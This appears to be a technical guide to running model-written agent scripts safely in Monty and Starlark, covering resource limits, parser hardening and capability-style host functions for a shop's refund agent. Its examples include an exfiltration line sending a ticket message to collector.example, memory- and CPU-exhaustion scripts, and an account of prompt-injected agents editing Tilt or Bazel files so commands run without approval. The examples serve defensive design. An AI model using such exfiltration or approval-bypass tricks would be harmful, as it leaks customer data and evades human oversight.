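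File access works similarly. Monty's `open` function only sends a request to a separate component, which can read directories the host has made available. If the host has made none available and supplies no handler of its own, the script cannot read any file. Pydantic's *Security Model* lists this component and memory management as the two areas of the code that need the most careful review. The support agent needs no files, so the shop can avoid the risk from the file component by leaving file access disabled.

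In Python and on JavaScript servers, Monty normally runs scripts in worker processes separate from the host. Each worker starts with an empty environment, so its memory does not contain the host's environment variables, and a crash in the worker does not crash the host. But Monty reuses each worker for up to 1,000 sessions by default, so a script that took control of one might see later users' data. Pydantic recommends one session per worker when users do not trust one another. The Rust library can also run scripts inside the host's process, where a crash would crash the host.

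Pydantic's programming interface can also connect to a remote server, and that server may run ordinary CPython without any of Monty's protections. An auditor therefore has to check what the server is running.

### The clock and random numbers in Monty

By the definition used here, Monty is not hermetic in its default configuration. Every session can read the system clock, and the `random` module is seeded from the operating system's source of randomness. Scripts can also sleep for up to ten seconds at a time. The support script uses none of these features, but another script might choose a customer at random or word an email differently in the afternoon, and replaying it could give a different result.

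The host can remove all three sources of variation when it opens a session:

```python
policy = {
    "datetime": datetime(2026, 12, 1, 9, 0),
    "random_start": {"seed": 4471},
    "sleep": "zero",
}
with pool.checkout(os_policy=policy) as session:
    session.feed_run(script)
```

The first setting fixes the date and time and freezes the timers that a script could use to measure how long a host function takes. The second makes the sequence of random numbers the same on every run. The third makes calls to sleep return immediately.

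Another setting, `call_host`, sends requests for the time and for random seeds to a handler in the host. Pydantic's ready-made handler returns values from the host's real clock and entropy source, so this setting alone does not make them repeatable. When a host resumes a saved session, Monty applies the new session's settings, so a script that started with a frozen clock may continue with a live one.

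Pydantic describes the clock as a weak capability, but the defaults matter for auditing. To rerun a script exactly, a host must either freeze the clock and fix the seed from the first run or record the original values, because it cannot recover them later.

### Absent features and filtered ones

A developer can also keep CPython and try to block its dangerous parts. This keeps ordinary libraries available and lets models use a language they write well. But the filter has to block every escape route through Python's reflection, whereas Monty functions expose only their type annotations and have no `__globals__` attribute.

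Hugging Face's agent library smolagents shows how a filter can fail. Its local executor walks a script's syntax tree and refuses forbidden operations, but the script's values are still ordinary CPython objects. OSV's *Sandbox escape in smolagents Local Python execution environment via dunder attributes* (2025), an entry in a public vulnerability database, records the flaw as CVE-2025-9959. The executor did not fully check attributes whose names begin and end with two underscores, so a script could use them to escape the sandbox. An attacker first had to use prompt injection to make the model write such a script. Version 1.21.0 fixed the problem.

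PraisonAI, another agent framework, had a similar flaw. According to GitLab's *GHSA-pv2j-rghr-v5r9* (2026), published on 18 June, its code tool advertised three layers of protection but used only two by default. One was a filter that searched the syntax tree for forbidden names, and the other replaced some built-in functions with guarded versions. CPython's internal C code can read attributes without calling those guarded functions, and the filter did not cover that route, so a script could read every attribute the filter was supposed to block. GitLab rated the flaw as medium severity, with a serious effect on confidentiality but none on data integrity. The developers fixed it in version 1.6.59.

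The two advisories show that a filter's authors must understand every part of an interpreter that other people wrote and continue to change. PraisonAI had two active layers, but neither covered CPython's internal route. Two advisories are too few to show how often filters fail. Starlark and Monty may also have bugs, because authors of a new interpreter know what it contains but can still make mistakes, especially in the parts that manage memory or pass values to the host.

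Monty has had much less time under attack than CPython. Pydantic reported early on that people had tried hard to escape it and failed, but added that real hardness "comes with time and stress". Pydantic now runs a bounty programme for reported escapes.

### Start-up time

Pydantic advertises that getting a new sandbox takes 0.80 ms with *Monty*, compared with 195 ms for a Docker container and 1,500 ms for a sandboxing service. Pydantic took these measurements itself, and they compare a Monty pool that is already running with alternatives that start from scratch. Its *Comparison to Alternatives* gives the method and several further figures. Each figure is the time from requesting a sandbox to receiving a first result, which for Monty is the answer to `1 + 1`.

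| Sandbox | What Pydantic timed | Time |
|---|---|---|
| Monty | New session from a running pool | 0.80 ms |
| Starlark in Rust | First evaluation, in the host's process | 1.3 ms |
| Monty | New pool and session | 5 ms |
| CPython in WebAssembly | New instance, compiled in advance | 16 ms |
| Docker | New container, image already downloaded | 195 ms |
| Daytona, a remote service | New sandbox in Europe, called from London | 1,500 ms |

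When both start cold, Monty is about 40 times faster than Docker, not about 240 times. Monty's 0.80 ms is a rounded median of 20 runs, while most of the other figures are single samples taken on one Apple laptop in September 2026. Docker on a Mac runs containers inside a Linux virtual machine, so a Linux server could give a different result. Daytona advertises sandbox creation in under 90 ms, but Pydantic could not reproduce this with default settings.

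Keeping sandboxes ready would also speed up the slower options. Pydantic measured about 40 ms for each call to an existing Daytona sandbox. But a host that follows Pydantic's advice to use a new Monty worker for every session cannot rely on the 0.80 ms figure, because starting each worker also takes time.

These differences in start-up time would rarely matter for the support agent. A weather query that Pydantic ran in code mode took 9.1 seconds from question to answer. A Docker start would have added about 2% to that time, and a Daytona start about 16%. Start-up time matters more when an agent runs dozens of short scripts per request, or when a host serves too many users to run a container for each.

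Starlark in Rust needs only about 0.01 ms for each evaluation after the first, though without a separate worker process to contain crashes.

### Dhall, Jsonnet and CEL

Dhall, Jsonnet and CEL are restricted languages that do not resemble Python, and none is a sensible choice for orchestrating tool calls. Dhall is a typed configuration language in which every program ends, but its scripts have no ordinary way to call a host function, and its imports can read files, web addresses and environment variables unless the host disables them. Jsonnet extends JSON with functions and can call functions that the host registers. However, it calculates a value only when something needs it, so a script that called a refund function without using the result might never issue the refund. CEL, Google's Common Expression Language, can also call host functions, but it evaluates one expression at a time and has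 no statements for carrying out a series of actions. Any of the three could produce a list of calls for the host to carry out, provided that no call depended on the result of an earlier one. CEL is better suited to checking a single call, for example with the rule `amount <= ticket.amount_paid`.

### Decision table

The table assumes that a model writes the scripts and nobody reviews them before they run.

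| What the host needs | Suitable choice | What to check first |
|---|---|---|
| Short tool-calling scripts in a Go application | Starlark in Go | `While` and `Recursion` are off, including in the older shared settings |
| The same, with a memory cap inside the process | Canonical's fork | Every host function's declarations are correct |
| Short scripts in a Java application | Bazel's interpreter, directly or through VGS | Identifiers fit the dialect's integer range |
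| Starlark in a Rust application, or in Python through starlark-pyo3 | Starlark in Rust | Loaded names stay private, and something limits recursive scripts |
| Classes, exceptions or standard modules in a Python or JavaScript application | Monty | Limits are set, since they are off by default; clock and seed are fixed if scripts must be repeatable |
| Third-party Python packages | CPython in a container or a remote sandbox | Network and file access are restricted from outside |
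| A yes-or-no rule about one call | CEL | The host supplies all the data that the rule needs |
| Full Python inside the host's process | No safe choice here | Filtered CPython is not enough for untrusted scripts |

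## Limiting time and memory

A mistake in one line of a script could take the shop's support desk offline, whichever interpreter the shop chose. Neither of these functions calls a host function or breaks any of Starlark's rules:

```python
def count():
    total = 0
    for a in range(1000000):
        for b in range(1000000):
            for c in range(1000000):
                total = total + 1

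def double():
    text = "x"
    for i in range(40):
        text = text + text
```

`count` runs its last line 10^18 times. At a hundred million times a second, that would take more than 300 years, although the function uses almost no memory and is certain to finish. `double` performs only forty operations, but its final string would take 2^40 bytes, or about 1.1 terabytes. The string reaches 16 GiB at the 34th doubling, which is more memory than many servers have to spare.

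Models are more likely to write milder versions of these. For example, a script that looked for duplicate complaints by comparing every ticket with every other would make about ten billion comparisons if the host supplied a list of 100,000 tickets.

### Lists that contain themselves

A script can also hang the interpreter without a long loop. These two lines create a list whose only item is the list itself:

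```python
knot = []
knot.append(knot)
```

The ban on recursion covers only functions that the script defines, so it does not prevent the endless loop that Starlark in Go warns about in such cases. A built-in operator that works through nested lists is written in Go, and it calls itself for each list it finds inside another.

According to its reference, the Starlark Go package limits operators such as `==` and `<` to a depth of 10 in nested values, so comparing two lists like `knot` produces an error. A type that the host defines has to pass on the remaining depth when it compares its own contents. If it calls the ordinary comparison function instead, the limit starts again at 10 each time, and a cyclic value could make the comparison recurse until the Go stack overflows and the process ends.

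A limit on depth does not restrict width, however:

```python
def nest():
    inner = [0] * 100
    for i in range(7):
        inner = [inner] * 100
    return inner

same = nest() == nest()
```

Each call to `nest` builds eight lists, and each outer list holds 100 references to the next inner one, so the call uses only 800 list slots. But if the interpreter compares the two results item by item, the single `==` requires 100^8, or 10^16, comparisons.

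### Two meanings of "safe"

The Starlark README's claim that untrusted code is safe to execute appears in its entry on hermetic execution, so "safe" there means that a script cannot read or change anything it was not given. These examples therefore do not contradict the claim.

A maintainer said the project had never claimed to be secure for untrusted code, because scripts could easily exhaust all memory or slow the host through hash flooding. In hash flooding, a script fills a dictionary with keys chosen to have the same hash value, so the interpreter has to search through many keys to find one. A user quoted this statement in issue 249 on Starlark's public tracker and asked whether it was right to expect that a script might crash a system but could not escape. Someone who replied worried that the README created unrealistic expectations about how well any particular interpreter would resist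 a malicious user.

The README describes what the language lets a script access, while the maintainer described what a script can do to its host process. Both can be correct, but the maintainer's statement is the better basis for planning if the host has to stay running.

### Counting steps

A step limit is the usual defence against functions like `count`. The Go interpreter compiles a script into small instructions, such as fetching a variable or adding two numbers, and counts them as it executes them. The host sets a maximum before the script starts. If the script exceeds it, the interpreter by default stops the script with the message "too many steps".

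The step count does not depend on how fast the machine is, so a script with the same inputs stops at the same point every time. This holds only within a single version of the interpreter. The Go source code does not specify exactly what a step is, and the definition may change (Bazel, 2017).

The limit applies to an interpreter thread, so scripts that the host runs on the same thread share one allowance. If the host's loader creates a new thread for each module, each module's step count starts at zero, and the module has no limit until the loader sets one. A host can also register a function, `OnMaxSteps`, to run when a script reaches the limit. It replaces the default action, so if it only writes a log entry, the script keeps running.

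A recent change to Starlark in Go makes the interpreter check the limit only at back-edges, where a program jumps back to an earlier instruction, as it does after each pass through a loop. A host that upgrades should therefore test its limit on function calls as well as loops. A chain of forty functions, each calling the next twice, makes about a trillion calls without a loop.

Steps are a poor measure of time because one step can do a great deal of work. This function removes duplicates from a list of email addresses, and a model might well write it:

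```python
def unique(addresses):
    seen = []
    for address in addresses:
        if address not in seen:
            seen.append(address)
    return seen
```

With 50,000 different addresses, the loop might use ten to fifteen steps per address, or at most 750,000 in total. But each `not in` counts as one step, even though it compares the address with everything already in `seen`, so the function makes about 1.25 billion comparisons. The `==` in the previous example is also one step, and the interpreter never gets to the next one, so a lower step limit would not help there.

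### Stopping a script from outside

The host can also cancel a running script. In Go, another part of the program waits for a deadline and then calls `Cancel` on the interpreter thread. This sets a variable that the interpreter checks from time to time. At the next check, the interpreter stops the script with an error. The thread stays cancelled until the host resets it.

`Cancel` has no immediate effect while the script is inside a built-in function, because the interpreter cannot check the variable until that function returns. If the shop cancels scripts after ten seconds but its mail server takes a minute to respond, a script that calls `mail.send` would run for about a minute. To avoid this, the host can attach its cancellation signal to the thread, so that `mail.send` can check it and return early. Operators that run for a long time inside the interpreter, such as the wide comparison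 above, have no such signal to check.

A host needs both a step limit and a way to cancel a running script. The step limit is better for stopping long computations because it stops them at a repeatable point, which makes the problem easier to investigate. Cancellation is better when a script is waiting, since it may use very few steps in a long time.

### Counting memory before using it

Neither a step limit nor a deadline reliably stops `double`. Its forty passes take only a few hundred steps, and on a fast machine it could exhaust memory before the deadline. Starlark in Go rejects single allocations that are unreasonably large, but has no way to limit a script's total memory. In Bazel's published source code, the `+` operator joins two strings without first checking the size of the result.

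Measuring how much memory a script currently holds is difficult in Go. Several threads may share the same frozen values, so it isn't clear which script's total should include them. The interpreter would also have to trace references through both Starlark values and the host's Go data, which the garbage collector normally does.

Canonical's fork takes a simpler approach and keeps an estimate of what each script allocates. Before an operation creates a value, the interpreter works out how large the value will be and adds that to the script's total:

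```python
new_size = len(left) + len(right)
if used + new_size > budget:
    stop_script("out of memory")
used = used + new_size
result = join(left, right)
```

These lines check the total before the interpreter joins the strings, because the join could crash the process before a later check ran. The estimate can be too high, since the script may already have discarded some of the values in the total. Overestimating is safer than underestimating, but it may stop a legitimate script that creates many short-lived strings.

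### What host functions declare

An interpreter can count its own work this way, but not the memory or time a host function uses. For those, Canonical's fork relies on four declarations by the function's author, and a host can require any combination of them.

| Declaration | What the function's author promises | How `tickets.read` could break the promise |
|---|---|---|
| `MemSafe` | The function adds the memory it allocates to the script's total | It returns a ticket with a 50 MB message and counts nothing |
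| `CPUSafe` | The function adds its computation to the script's steps | It searches a million tickets in memory but counts one step |
| `TimeSafe` | The function stops promptly when the host cancels the script | It waits for a slow database and ignores cancellation |
| `IOSafe` | The function does not use files, the network or similar resources on its own | It queries a database |

On a strict reading, none of the shop's three functions can declare `IOSafe`, since their purpose is to reach a database, a payment service and a mail server. The shop could require the other three declarations and control outside access by choosing which functions to provide.

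These declarations are most useful when several people add functions to a host. A developer who adds a function without thinking about limits will get an error the first time a script calls it, instead of an outage months later.

### Bifrost's limits

Bifrost runs scripts on Canonical's version of Starlark inside the gateway process and gives each run its own budget. An operator can change any of the default limits without restarting the gateway.

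| Limit | Default | What it covers |
|---|---|---|
| Source code | 64 KiB | The script that the model submits |
| Steps | 1,000,000 | Computation, including work inside built-in functions |
| Memory | 64 MiB | Estimated allocations, checked before they happen |
| Printed output | 64 KiB | Text from `print`, plus short notes about failed calls |
| Tool calls | 64 | Calls to connected servers during one run |
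| Value size | 1 MiB | Each value that enters or leaves the script |
| Nesting depth | 64 | Lists and dictionaries that enter or leave the script |
| Time | 30 seconds | Each tool call, and also the whole run |

The step limit stops `count`. Each pass through the innermost loop takes more than one step, so the script reaches a million steps before that loop gets through its million numbers once. This should take well under a second, far less than the 30-second limit.

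The memory limit stops `double` by the 26th doubling, when the string would reach 64 MiB. If the estimate also includes the earlier, shorter strings, the limit stops the script one doubling sooner. If Bifrost counts one step for each character copied, the script would run out of steps even earlier, around the 19th doubling, when the string is about half a megabyte. The limit of 1 MiB per value doesn't apply here, because it covers only values that pass between the script and the gateway.

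The support script uses three tool calls and a few dozen steps, so it fits easily within the limits. A script that refunded thirty tickets would need ninety calls. With a limit of 64, it would complete 21 refunds, read the 22nd ticket, and stop when it tried to pay that refund. With a limit of 65, it would pay the 22nd customer but fail to send the email. These limits can interrupt a job at any point, so an operator should set them for the largest job that staff will reasonably request.

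When a tool call takes too long, the Bifrost gateway stops the script and returns an error, but the server handling the call may still finish the work. If `orders.refund` times out, the customer may or may not have received the money, and neither the model nor the gateway has a result showing which. If the model then writes a new script to retry the refund, the shop may pay twice.

Bifrost's limits apply to each script separately. A model that receives a "too many steps" error can keep submitting slightly different scripts, each of which can use another million steps, so the host also needs to limit how many scripts one request may run.

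Drone, a service that builds and tests software, limits its Starlark configuration files to 50,000 steps by default, though administrators can raise the limit. This would stop `count` about twenty times sooner than Bifrost's limit if both products counted steps the same way, but they may not, since Bifrost includes work inside built-in functions. A limit of 50,000 makes sense for configuration, which usually produces a short description of a job, but it would be tight for an agent that processes data. At ten steps per record, a script could examine only 5,000 records under Drone's limit, compared with 100,000 under Bifrost's. Neither limit alone protects against `double` if the interpreter counts joining two strings as a single step.

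### Parsing comes before counting

Bifrost describes its limits as cooperative because they depend on the interpreter and built-in functions to count their own work, and the operating system does not enforce them. Work they do not count falls outside the budget, and the first such work is reading the script.

The interpreter has to parse a script before running it, turning the text into a structure of statements and expressions. A parser usually handles brackets by calling itself. For the text `[[[1]]]`, it starts reading a list, finds another list inside, and calls itself to read that one. Each level uses some of the stack, the memory in which a program keeps track of unfinished calls. An attacker can exhaust the stack before the script starts running by submitting a file with an enormous number of opening brackets.

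The Go interpreter had this flaw, which its developers recorded as security advisory GHSA-wcqm-92f8-mh2v. According to the commit that fixed it, Starlark in Go's *syntax*, both the parser and the scanner (the part that splits text into words and symbols) could overflow the stack and crash the application. The interpreter's existing limit on call depth applied only to running scripts. The parser and scanner now also reject input that is nested too deeply. The developers added a test that examines which parser functions call one another and fails if any can recurse without passing through the new depth counter. This should catch the same mistake if someone adds new syntax later.

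Experienced language developers make this mistake often enough that a host should expect it. Go's *Vulnerability Report* (2024) describes the same kind of crash in the standard library's parser for Go code. Rhai's *Safety and Protection Against DOS Attacks*, part of the manual for an embedded language written in Rust, lists deeply nested expressions and very large literals among the ways a script can exhaust the stack during parsing. It also lists modules that load themselves, which a Starlark host has to prevent in its own loader by tracking which modules it has started but not finished loading.

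Limiting source size also limits nesting depth, since each level needs at least one character. Bifrost's 64 KiB limit allows at most 65,536 opening brackets. On a 64-bit machine, Go by default lets a single stack grow to about 1 GB, so each bracket would have to use more than 15 KB of stack to cause an overflow. That seems unlikely, but the parser could still use far more memory than the script's 64 MiB budget. A host without a size limit depends entirely on the fix, and a fork of the interpreter has the fix only if its maintainers have merged it.

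Pydantic's Monty handles the same problem by scanning any script longer than 4 KiB for deep nesting before parsing it. Shorter scripts can add at most a few megabytes of stack that the memory limit does not count. Monty's limits on running time also exclude compilation time.

### Work in the host and many scripts at once

Tool servers and the connections to them are also outside Bifrost's budget. If a server sent a 500 MB response, the connection might hold all of it in the gateway's memory before Bifrost could check it against its 1 MiB limit. The connection therefore needs its own size limit. Monty has a similar gap when a host gives scripts an in-memory file system. The host process stores these files, and the script's memory limit does not apply there, so Pydantic caps their total size separately, at 50 MB by default.

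The memory limit applies to each script separately, and Bifrost doesn't limit how many scripts run at the same time, so 100 scripts could together allocate 6.25 GiB without any of them exceeding the default 64 MiB. If the operator raised the limit to 256 MiB because one script needed more memory, 100 scripts could allocate 25 GiB. A host that can spare 2 GiB should run no more than 32 scripts at once under the default limit, and fewer in practice, because the estimates leave out some of the memory the process uses. Further scripts can wait in a queue.

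For hosts that face deliberate attacks, Starlark in Go considers a separate process with limits set by the operating system the only reliable defence.

### Clocks that pause

The effect of a time limit depends on which clock it uses. Monty's main time limit counts only the time a script spends executing, so the clock pauses while the script waits for a host function to return. If `orders.refund` takes twenty seconds, a script with a five-second limit can still finish, though the member of staff waits more than twenty seconds for an answer.

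Without the pause, a script that waits overnight for a manager's approval would run out of time before morning. But with the pause, the limit does little to restrict how many calls a script makes. A script that catches errors could keep retrying a refund that the host rejects. If each attempt used ten microseconds of execution, a five-second limit would allow 500,000 attempts.

Monty has four settings that together cover most of these cases:

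| Setting | What it measures | When it starts again |
|---|---|---|
| `max_feed_duration_secs` | Execution time | With each new piece of code |
| `max_turn_duration_secs` | Execution time | After each answer from the host |
| `request_timeout` | Ordinary clock time | After each answer from the host |
| `max_suspensions` | Number of times the script pauses, including for host calls | With each new session |

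The second and third settings cannot stop the refund loop, because every rejection restarts them. `max_suspensions` stops it after a fixed number of attempts. The interpreter checks its execution limits only at certain points, so an operation that never reaches one could run indefinitely. `request_timeout` lets the host end the worker process from outside in that case, but it is off by default for local workers. Pydantic recommends setting it and at least one of the execution limits for untrusted code. A host function that might hang needs its own timeout.

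When Monty stops a script for exceeding its memory or time limit, the values left in the session may be corrupted. Monty does not close the session automatically, so the host can still send it code, and that code may appear to work while using the corrupted values. The host has to discard the session itself.

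## Deciding which host functions to expose

How much damage a script can do depends mostly on which host functions it can call, and the interpreter cannot make a badly chosen function safe. A script that stays within every time and memory limit can still cost the shop thousands of dollars, because `orders.refund` pays any amount on any order.

### From the script to the payment service

Suppose a script running in the Go interpreter reaches `orders.refund("A-1093", 4500)`. The interpreter looks up `orders`, fetches its `refund` attribute and evaluates the two arguments. It then calls a Go function that the shop's developer wrote:

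```go
func refund(thread *starlark.Thread, b *starlark.Builtin,
	args starlark.Tuple, kwargs []starlark.Tuple) (starlark.Value, error) {
	var orderID string
	var amount int
	if err := starlark.UnpackArgs(b.Name(), args, kwargs,
		"order_id", &orderID, "amount", &amount); err != nil {
		return nil, err
	}
	// The shop's own checks belong here.
	if err := payments.Refund(orderID, amount); err != nil {
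		return nil, errors.New("refund failed")
	}
	return starlark.None, nil
}
```

Every host function in Go takes the interpreter thread, the function's own record, the positional arguments and the keyword arguments as parameters. It returns either a value or an error.

`UnpackArgs` copies the script's arguments into Go variables and checks their types. It can check for types including booleans, integers, strings, lists, dictionaries and functions, according to a copy of the source code that NetApp publishes. If a script passes the amount as `"45.00"`, the call fails before any money moves. But `UnpackArgs` accepts -4500 and 4,500,000 as well as 4500, and any text as an order number.

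A host can also define a type with its own unpacking rule. The shop could create an `OrderID` type that rejects text in the wrong format and use it in every function that takes an order number. However, a correctly formatted number may still belong to someone else's order.

The shop's own checks belong in the host function, after it unpacks its arguments and before its first side effect, because every call passes through that point. A check in the script is weaker because the model may leave it out, and so is a rule in the function's description because the model may not follow it.

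`payments.Refund` then runs as ordinary Go code, with the support application's password and network access, while the script waits.

A host function must return a Starlark value. Starlark warns that Go's `nil` is not the same as Starlark's `None`, and that the Go compiler will not catch code that confuses them. If a ticket has no order number and `tickets.read` puts `nil` in that field of the dictionary, the host may crash when the script uses the field.

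Host functions that accept other functions need extra care because the script's code runs partway through them. Suppose the shop added `mail.send_all(addresses, make_body)`, which checks a list of addresses and then calls the script's `make_body` to write each message. `make_body` could change an address in the list after the check but before the host used it. The host should copy the list first, then check the copy and send only to the addresses in it.

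### What the interpreter cannot guarantee

Pydantic guarantees that a Monty script can reach only what the host exposes, but cannot guarantee that what the host exposes is safe. The same limit applies to Starlark and every other hermetic language. Luau, the version of Lua that the games company Roblox uses, has no functions for reading files or starting programs. Some hosts may still expose functions that are unsafe for untrusted code, so Luau adds features for keeping trusted and untrusted scripts apart.

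A function that fetches any web address gives a script a network connection. Suppose customers can attach photos of damaged goods to their tickets, and the shop adds `web.fetch(address)` so that scripts can retrieve them. A hostile script could write this:

```python
web.fetch("collector.example/?m=" + ticket["message"])
```

The request delivers the customer's message to whoever runs `collector.example`, even if the server returns an error. The same function could also reach servers inside the shop's network that trust any request from the support application.

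Checking the address correctly is hard. A rule that it must begin with `photos.shop.example` also accepts `photos.shop.example.attacker.example`, which belongs to a different site. Even a correct check on the site's name can fail if the server redirects the request to another site and the host follows the redirect. A function `ticket_photo(number)`, which returns a photo the shop has stored with the ticket, avoids the problem because it takes no address.

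Some hosts give scripts much more than this. One listed on pkg.go.dev, the documentation site for Go packages, makes parts of Go's standard library available to Starlark. Its examples fetch web pages, pause for two seconds and run a web server. A script that can call `http.Get` can reach the network, even though Starlark itself has no network operations.

### Capabilities and the confused deputy

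Capabilities date from research at MIT in the mid-1960s on computers that ran programs for many people at once. In that design, each running program has a list of capabilities. Each entry points to an object, such as a section of memory or a device, and records what the program may do with it. The program refers to objects by their position in the list, so it cannot refer to anything not on the list. It can start another program with a shorter list, or pass on read-only access to something it can also write, but it cannot pass on more access than it has.

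The design also has protected routines, which resemble host functions. A routine that updates a shared database, for example, runs with its own list of capabilities. Other programs can start it only at fixed entry points, so they can request an update but can't write to the database themselves. `orders.refund` protects the payment password in much the same way, but it lets the script choose both the order and the amount.

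Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* describes how a routine like this can go wrong. Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers, had a compiler that recorded usage statistics in a system directory, so the operators gave the compiler permission to write files there. Users could tell the compiler where to write debugging output, and one user supplied the name of the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. The user didn't have permission to change that file, but the compiler did, so it overwrote the billing records.

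Hardy calls the compiler a confused deputy because it acted with authority from two sources, the operators and the user, and could not specify which one it was using when it opened a file. He considers having the compiler reject names in the system directory, but some users might have good reason to write there. Rejecting only the billing file would require updating the compiler whenever a new sensitive file appeared. Tymshare let programs switch between the two sources of authority, but soon found programs that needed more than two. When Hardy last wrote down the rules for opening a file, they contained fourteen "and"s and "or"s.

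`orders.refund` can be confused in the same way. The support application has authority to refund any order, while the member of staff asked about only one. If a line in the customer's message tricks the model into passing a different order number, the function uses the application's authority to refund that order. The host could check whether this member of staff may issue refunds, but she would pass because her job includes refunding other customers, and the check wouldn't establish which order she meant.

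Hardy's solution is to give the compiler a capability for the statistics file and have each user pass it a capability for the output file. The user cannot pass a capability for the billing file because she does not have one.

Miller (2006), in *Robust Composition*, illustrates the difference with two Unix commands that copy a file:

```
cp foo.txt bar.txt
cat < foo.txt > bar.txt
```

`cp` takes two file names and opens the files itself, so it needs access to every file a user might name. When `cat` is used to copy a file, the shell opens both files and passes them to `cat`, which needs no other access, although ordinary Unix gives both programs all of the user's access anyway. `orders.refund(order_id, amount)` works like `cp` because it takes an order's ID and needs access to every order a script might name. To make it work like `cat`, the host has to choose the order before the script starts.

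Semgrep's *Security Like It's 1977* (2026) applies Hardy's story to AI agents, predicts that they will create many confused deputies, and recommends capabilities as the remedy. Semgrep has a commercial interest in this prediction because it sells security software, but the refund example does involve the mechanism Hardy described.

### A refund function for one order

In Python, with either Monty or starlark-pyo3, the narrower function is short:

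```python
def make_refund(ticket_id, customer_id, order_id, maximum):
    def refund(amount):
        if type(amount) is not int or amount <= 0:
            raise ValueError("amount must be a positive whole number of cents")
        if ticket_status(ticket_id) != "damage confirmed":
            raise ValueError("damage not confirmed")
        if not reserve(order_id, amount, maximum):
            raise ValueError("amount exceeds the refund limit")
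        payments.refund(customer_id, order_id, amount)
    return refund
```

The host calls `make_refund` when a member of staff makes a request about a ticket, and gives the script only the inner function, `refund`. That function already contains the customer, the order and the maximum, here the amount the customer paid. The script can choose only the amount. The host can prepare the email function in the same way, with the customer's address fixed, and supply the ticket as plain data. The support script then becomes:

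```python
def handle():
    if ticket["status"] != "damage confirmed":
        return "No refund: damage not confirmed"
    refund(ticket["amount_paid"])
    notify("We have refunded your order in full.")
    return "Refunded"

result = handle()
```

If the model leaves out the `if` statement, the shop no longer loses money, because `refund` checks the status itself. The check in the script is now needed only to return a clearer message.

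`reserve` records the amount in the shop's database before the payment, and returns `False` if the order's total would exceed the maximum. A variable inside `make_refund` would not be enough, because it would start again at zero if the model wrote a second script and the host created a new function for it. Two scripts running at once could both read the old total before either updated it, so `reserve` has to check and record the amount in a single database transaction. If the payment service times out, the amount stays reserved so that a retry cannot pay the customer twice. Staff have to release the reservation if the payment turns out to have failed.

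| What a hostile script tries | `orders.refund(order_id, amount)` | `refund(amount)` |
|---|---|---|
| Refund another customer's order | The shop pays | The script cannot name another order |
| Refund more than the customer paid | The shop pays, unless the payment service objects | Error |
| Refund the full amount repeatedly | The shop pays each time, unless the payment service objects | Error after the first refund |
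| Pass a negative amount | Depends on the payment service | Error |
| Refund before staff confirm the damage | The shop pays | Error |
| Refund in full when staff wanted to refund half | The shop pays | The shop pays, unless the host set a lower maximum |

Even if the payment service refuses to refund more than the price of an order, a script using the general function could refund 64 orders at $45 each within Bifrost's default limit of 64 tool calls. That totals $2,880, compared with $45 using the narrow function.

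The protection depends on where the host gets the ticket number. If the staff member has ticket 4471 open on her screen, the host can take the number from there, and a model that writes 4417 by mistake can no longer refund the wrong order. If the model extracts the number from her typed request, the host will create a function for whatever number the model gives, even if it is wrong. In that case, the host could first show her the customer's name so she can catch a mistake.

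Narrow functions are less convenient when nobody knows in advance which orders a request covers. For example, an employee might ask to refund everyone whose parcel was on a van that crashed. The host could provide a search function that returns the affected tickets, each with its own `refund` function. But the script could refund any ticket the search returned, so the host would have to restrict the search to that van's deliveries. A cap on total refunds for the request would limit the loss if the search returned the wrong tickets.

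A narrow function should also stop working when the request ends. A paused Monty script may resume the next morning, and a Starlark host may keep a script's functions and call them later, so the code may still hold `refund`. Miller describes a pattern called a caretaker, an object that forwards calls to another object only while its creator leaves a switch on. To implement this, `make_refund` would need one more variable, which the host sets to false when the staff member closes the ticket.

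### Indirect effects

A list of the functions a script can call does not show everything the script can cause. Miller distinguishes permission, which is direct access to an object, from authority, which includes effects caused through other objects. In his example, Bob lacks permission to write to a computer's password file, but Alice has it. If Bob can send Alice messages and she writes whatever he asks, he has authority to change the file.

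The shop could create this problem by exposing a function that looks harmless, such as `tickets.add_note(text)`. Suppose an older program runs every night and refunds each ticket whose notes contain the word "approved". A script that can add notes can then cause refunds, even without a refund function. The developer who reviews `add_note` has to know about the nightly program, which may be in a different codebase.

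### Running commands from Bazel, Tilt and shac

Several well-known tools give Starlark scripts a function that runs any command. Bazel provides `repository_ctx.execute` to the rules that fetch and prepare a project's external dependencies. These rules may have to detect which compiler a machine has, which Starlark alone cannot do. Bazel does not expose the function to ordinary BUILD files, so most of the build remains repeatable.

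Tilt, a tool that runs a project's services during development, has a configuration language with a function called `local`, which runs a shell command on the developer's machine and returns the output. Much of what Tilt is for is starting and inspecting local programs, so it would be hard to use without such a function.

In shac, `ctx.os.exec` lets checks run existing tools such as code formatters. Network access is blocked by default, but Fuchsia's documentation shows that a script can lift the block by passing `allow_network = True`, so it prevents only accidental access. Similarly, shac's `read_file` accepts only paths inside the project, but this doesn't limit which files a command started by the script can open, because the command doesn't go through `read_file`.

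These tools allow commands despite the risk because the people who write the files can already run them. A developer who puts a harmful command in her Tilt configuration could have typed it in a terminal instead. Colleagues who download the project take a risk, but they take the same one when they run its tests.

A model that writes a Starlark file may have fewer permissions than the tool that runs it. Many coding agents ask for approval before running a shell command but edit project files without asking. Tilt reruns its configuration file whenever it changes, so an agent could run a command without approval by adding a call to `local`. With Bazel and shac, the command would run at the next build or check, probably started by a person who didn't know the file had changed. Injected text in a web page or bug report could cause the agent to make such an edit.

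A team that uses these tools with a coding agent should either require approval for changes to files that can run commands or run the tools in a container without the developer's passwords. A developer building a new host for model-written scripts should leave out functions that run arbitrary commands. If scripts need a code formatter, the host can offer `format(text)`, which runs one fixed program with fixed options and passes it the text as input.

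### Objects and the things they lead to

An object can expose far more than a single function because it may have dozens of attributes and methods. Monty scripts can use a host object only if the developer wraps it. The wrapper exposes nothing by default, so the developer must list the attributes that scripts may read and the methods they may call. Pydantic's example is a bank account with an owner, a balance, and the methods `withdraw` and `close`. The wrapper allows `withdraw` but leaves out `close`, so a script cannot close the account.

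The list controls which methods a script can call, but not the arguments it passes. In Pydantic's example, `withdraw` subtracts the amount from the balance without checking the amount, so a script that withdrew -30 would add 30 to the balance. A real account class needs the same checks as `refund`.

Developers can also write `'all'` instead of listing names. Monty still hides names that begin with an underscore, and for methods it exposes only those that the class defines. Using `'all'` is convenient, but if a colleague later adds a `transfer` method to the class, scripts can call it immediately. An explicit list would keep the new method hidden until someone decided to expose it.

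Monty has looser rules for host modules, which scripts can import by name. If the developer supplies a module as a dictionary, Monty exposes every public item in it. Host modules also remain available for the whole session, whereas the host supplies functions again with each piece of code. If a session will handle several tickets, a function tied to one ticket should therefore not go into a module.

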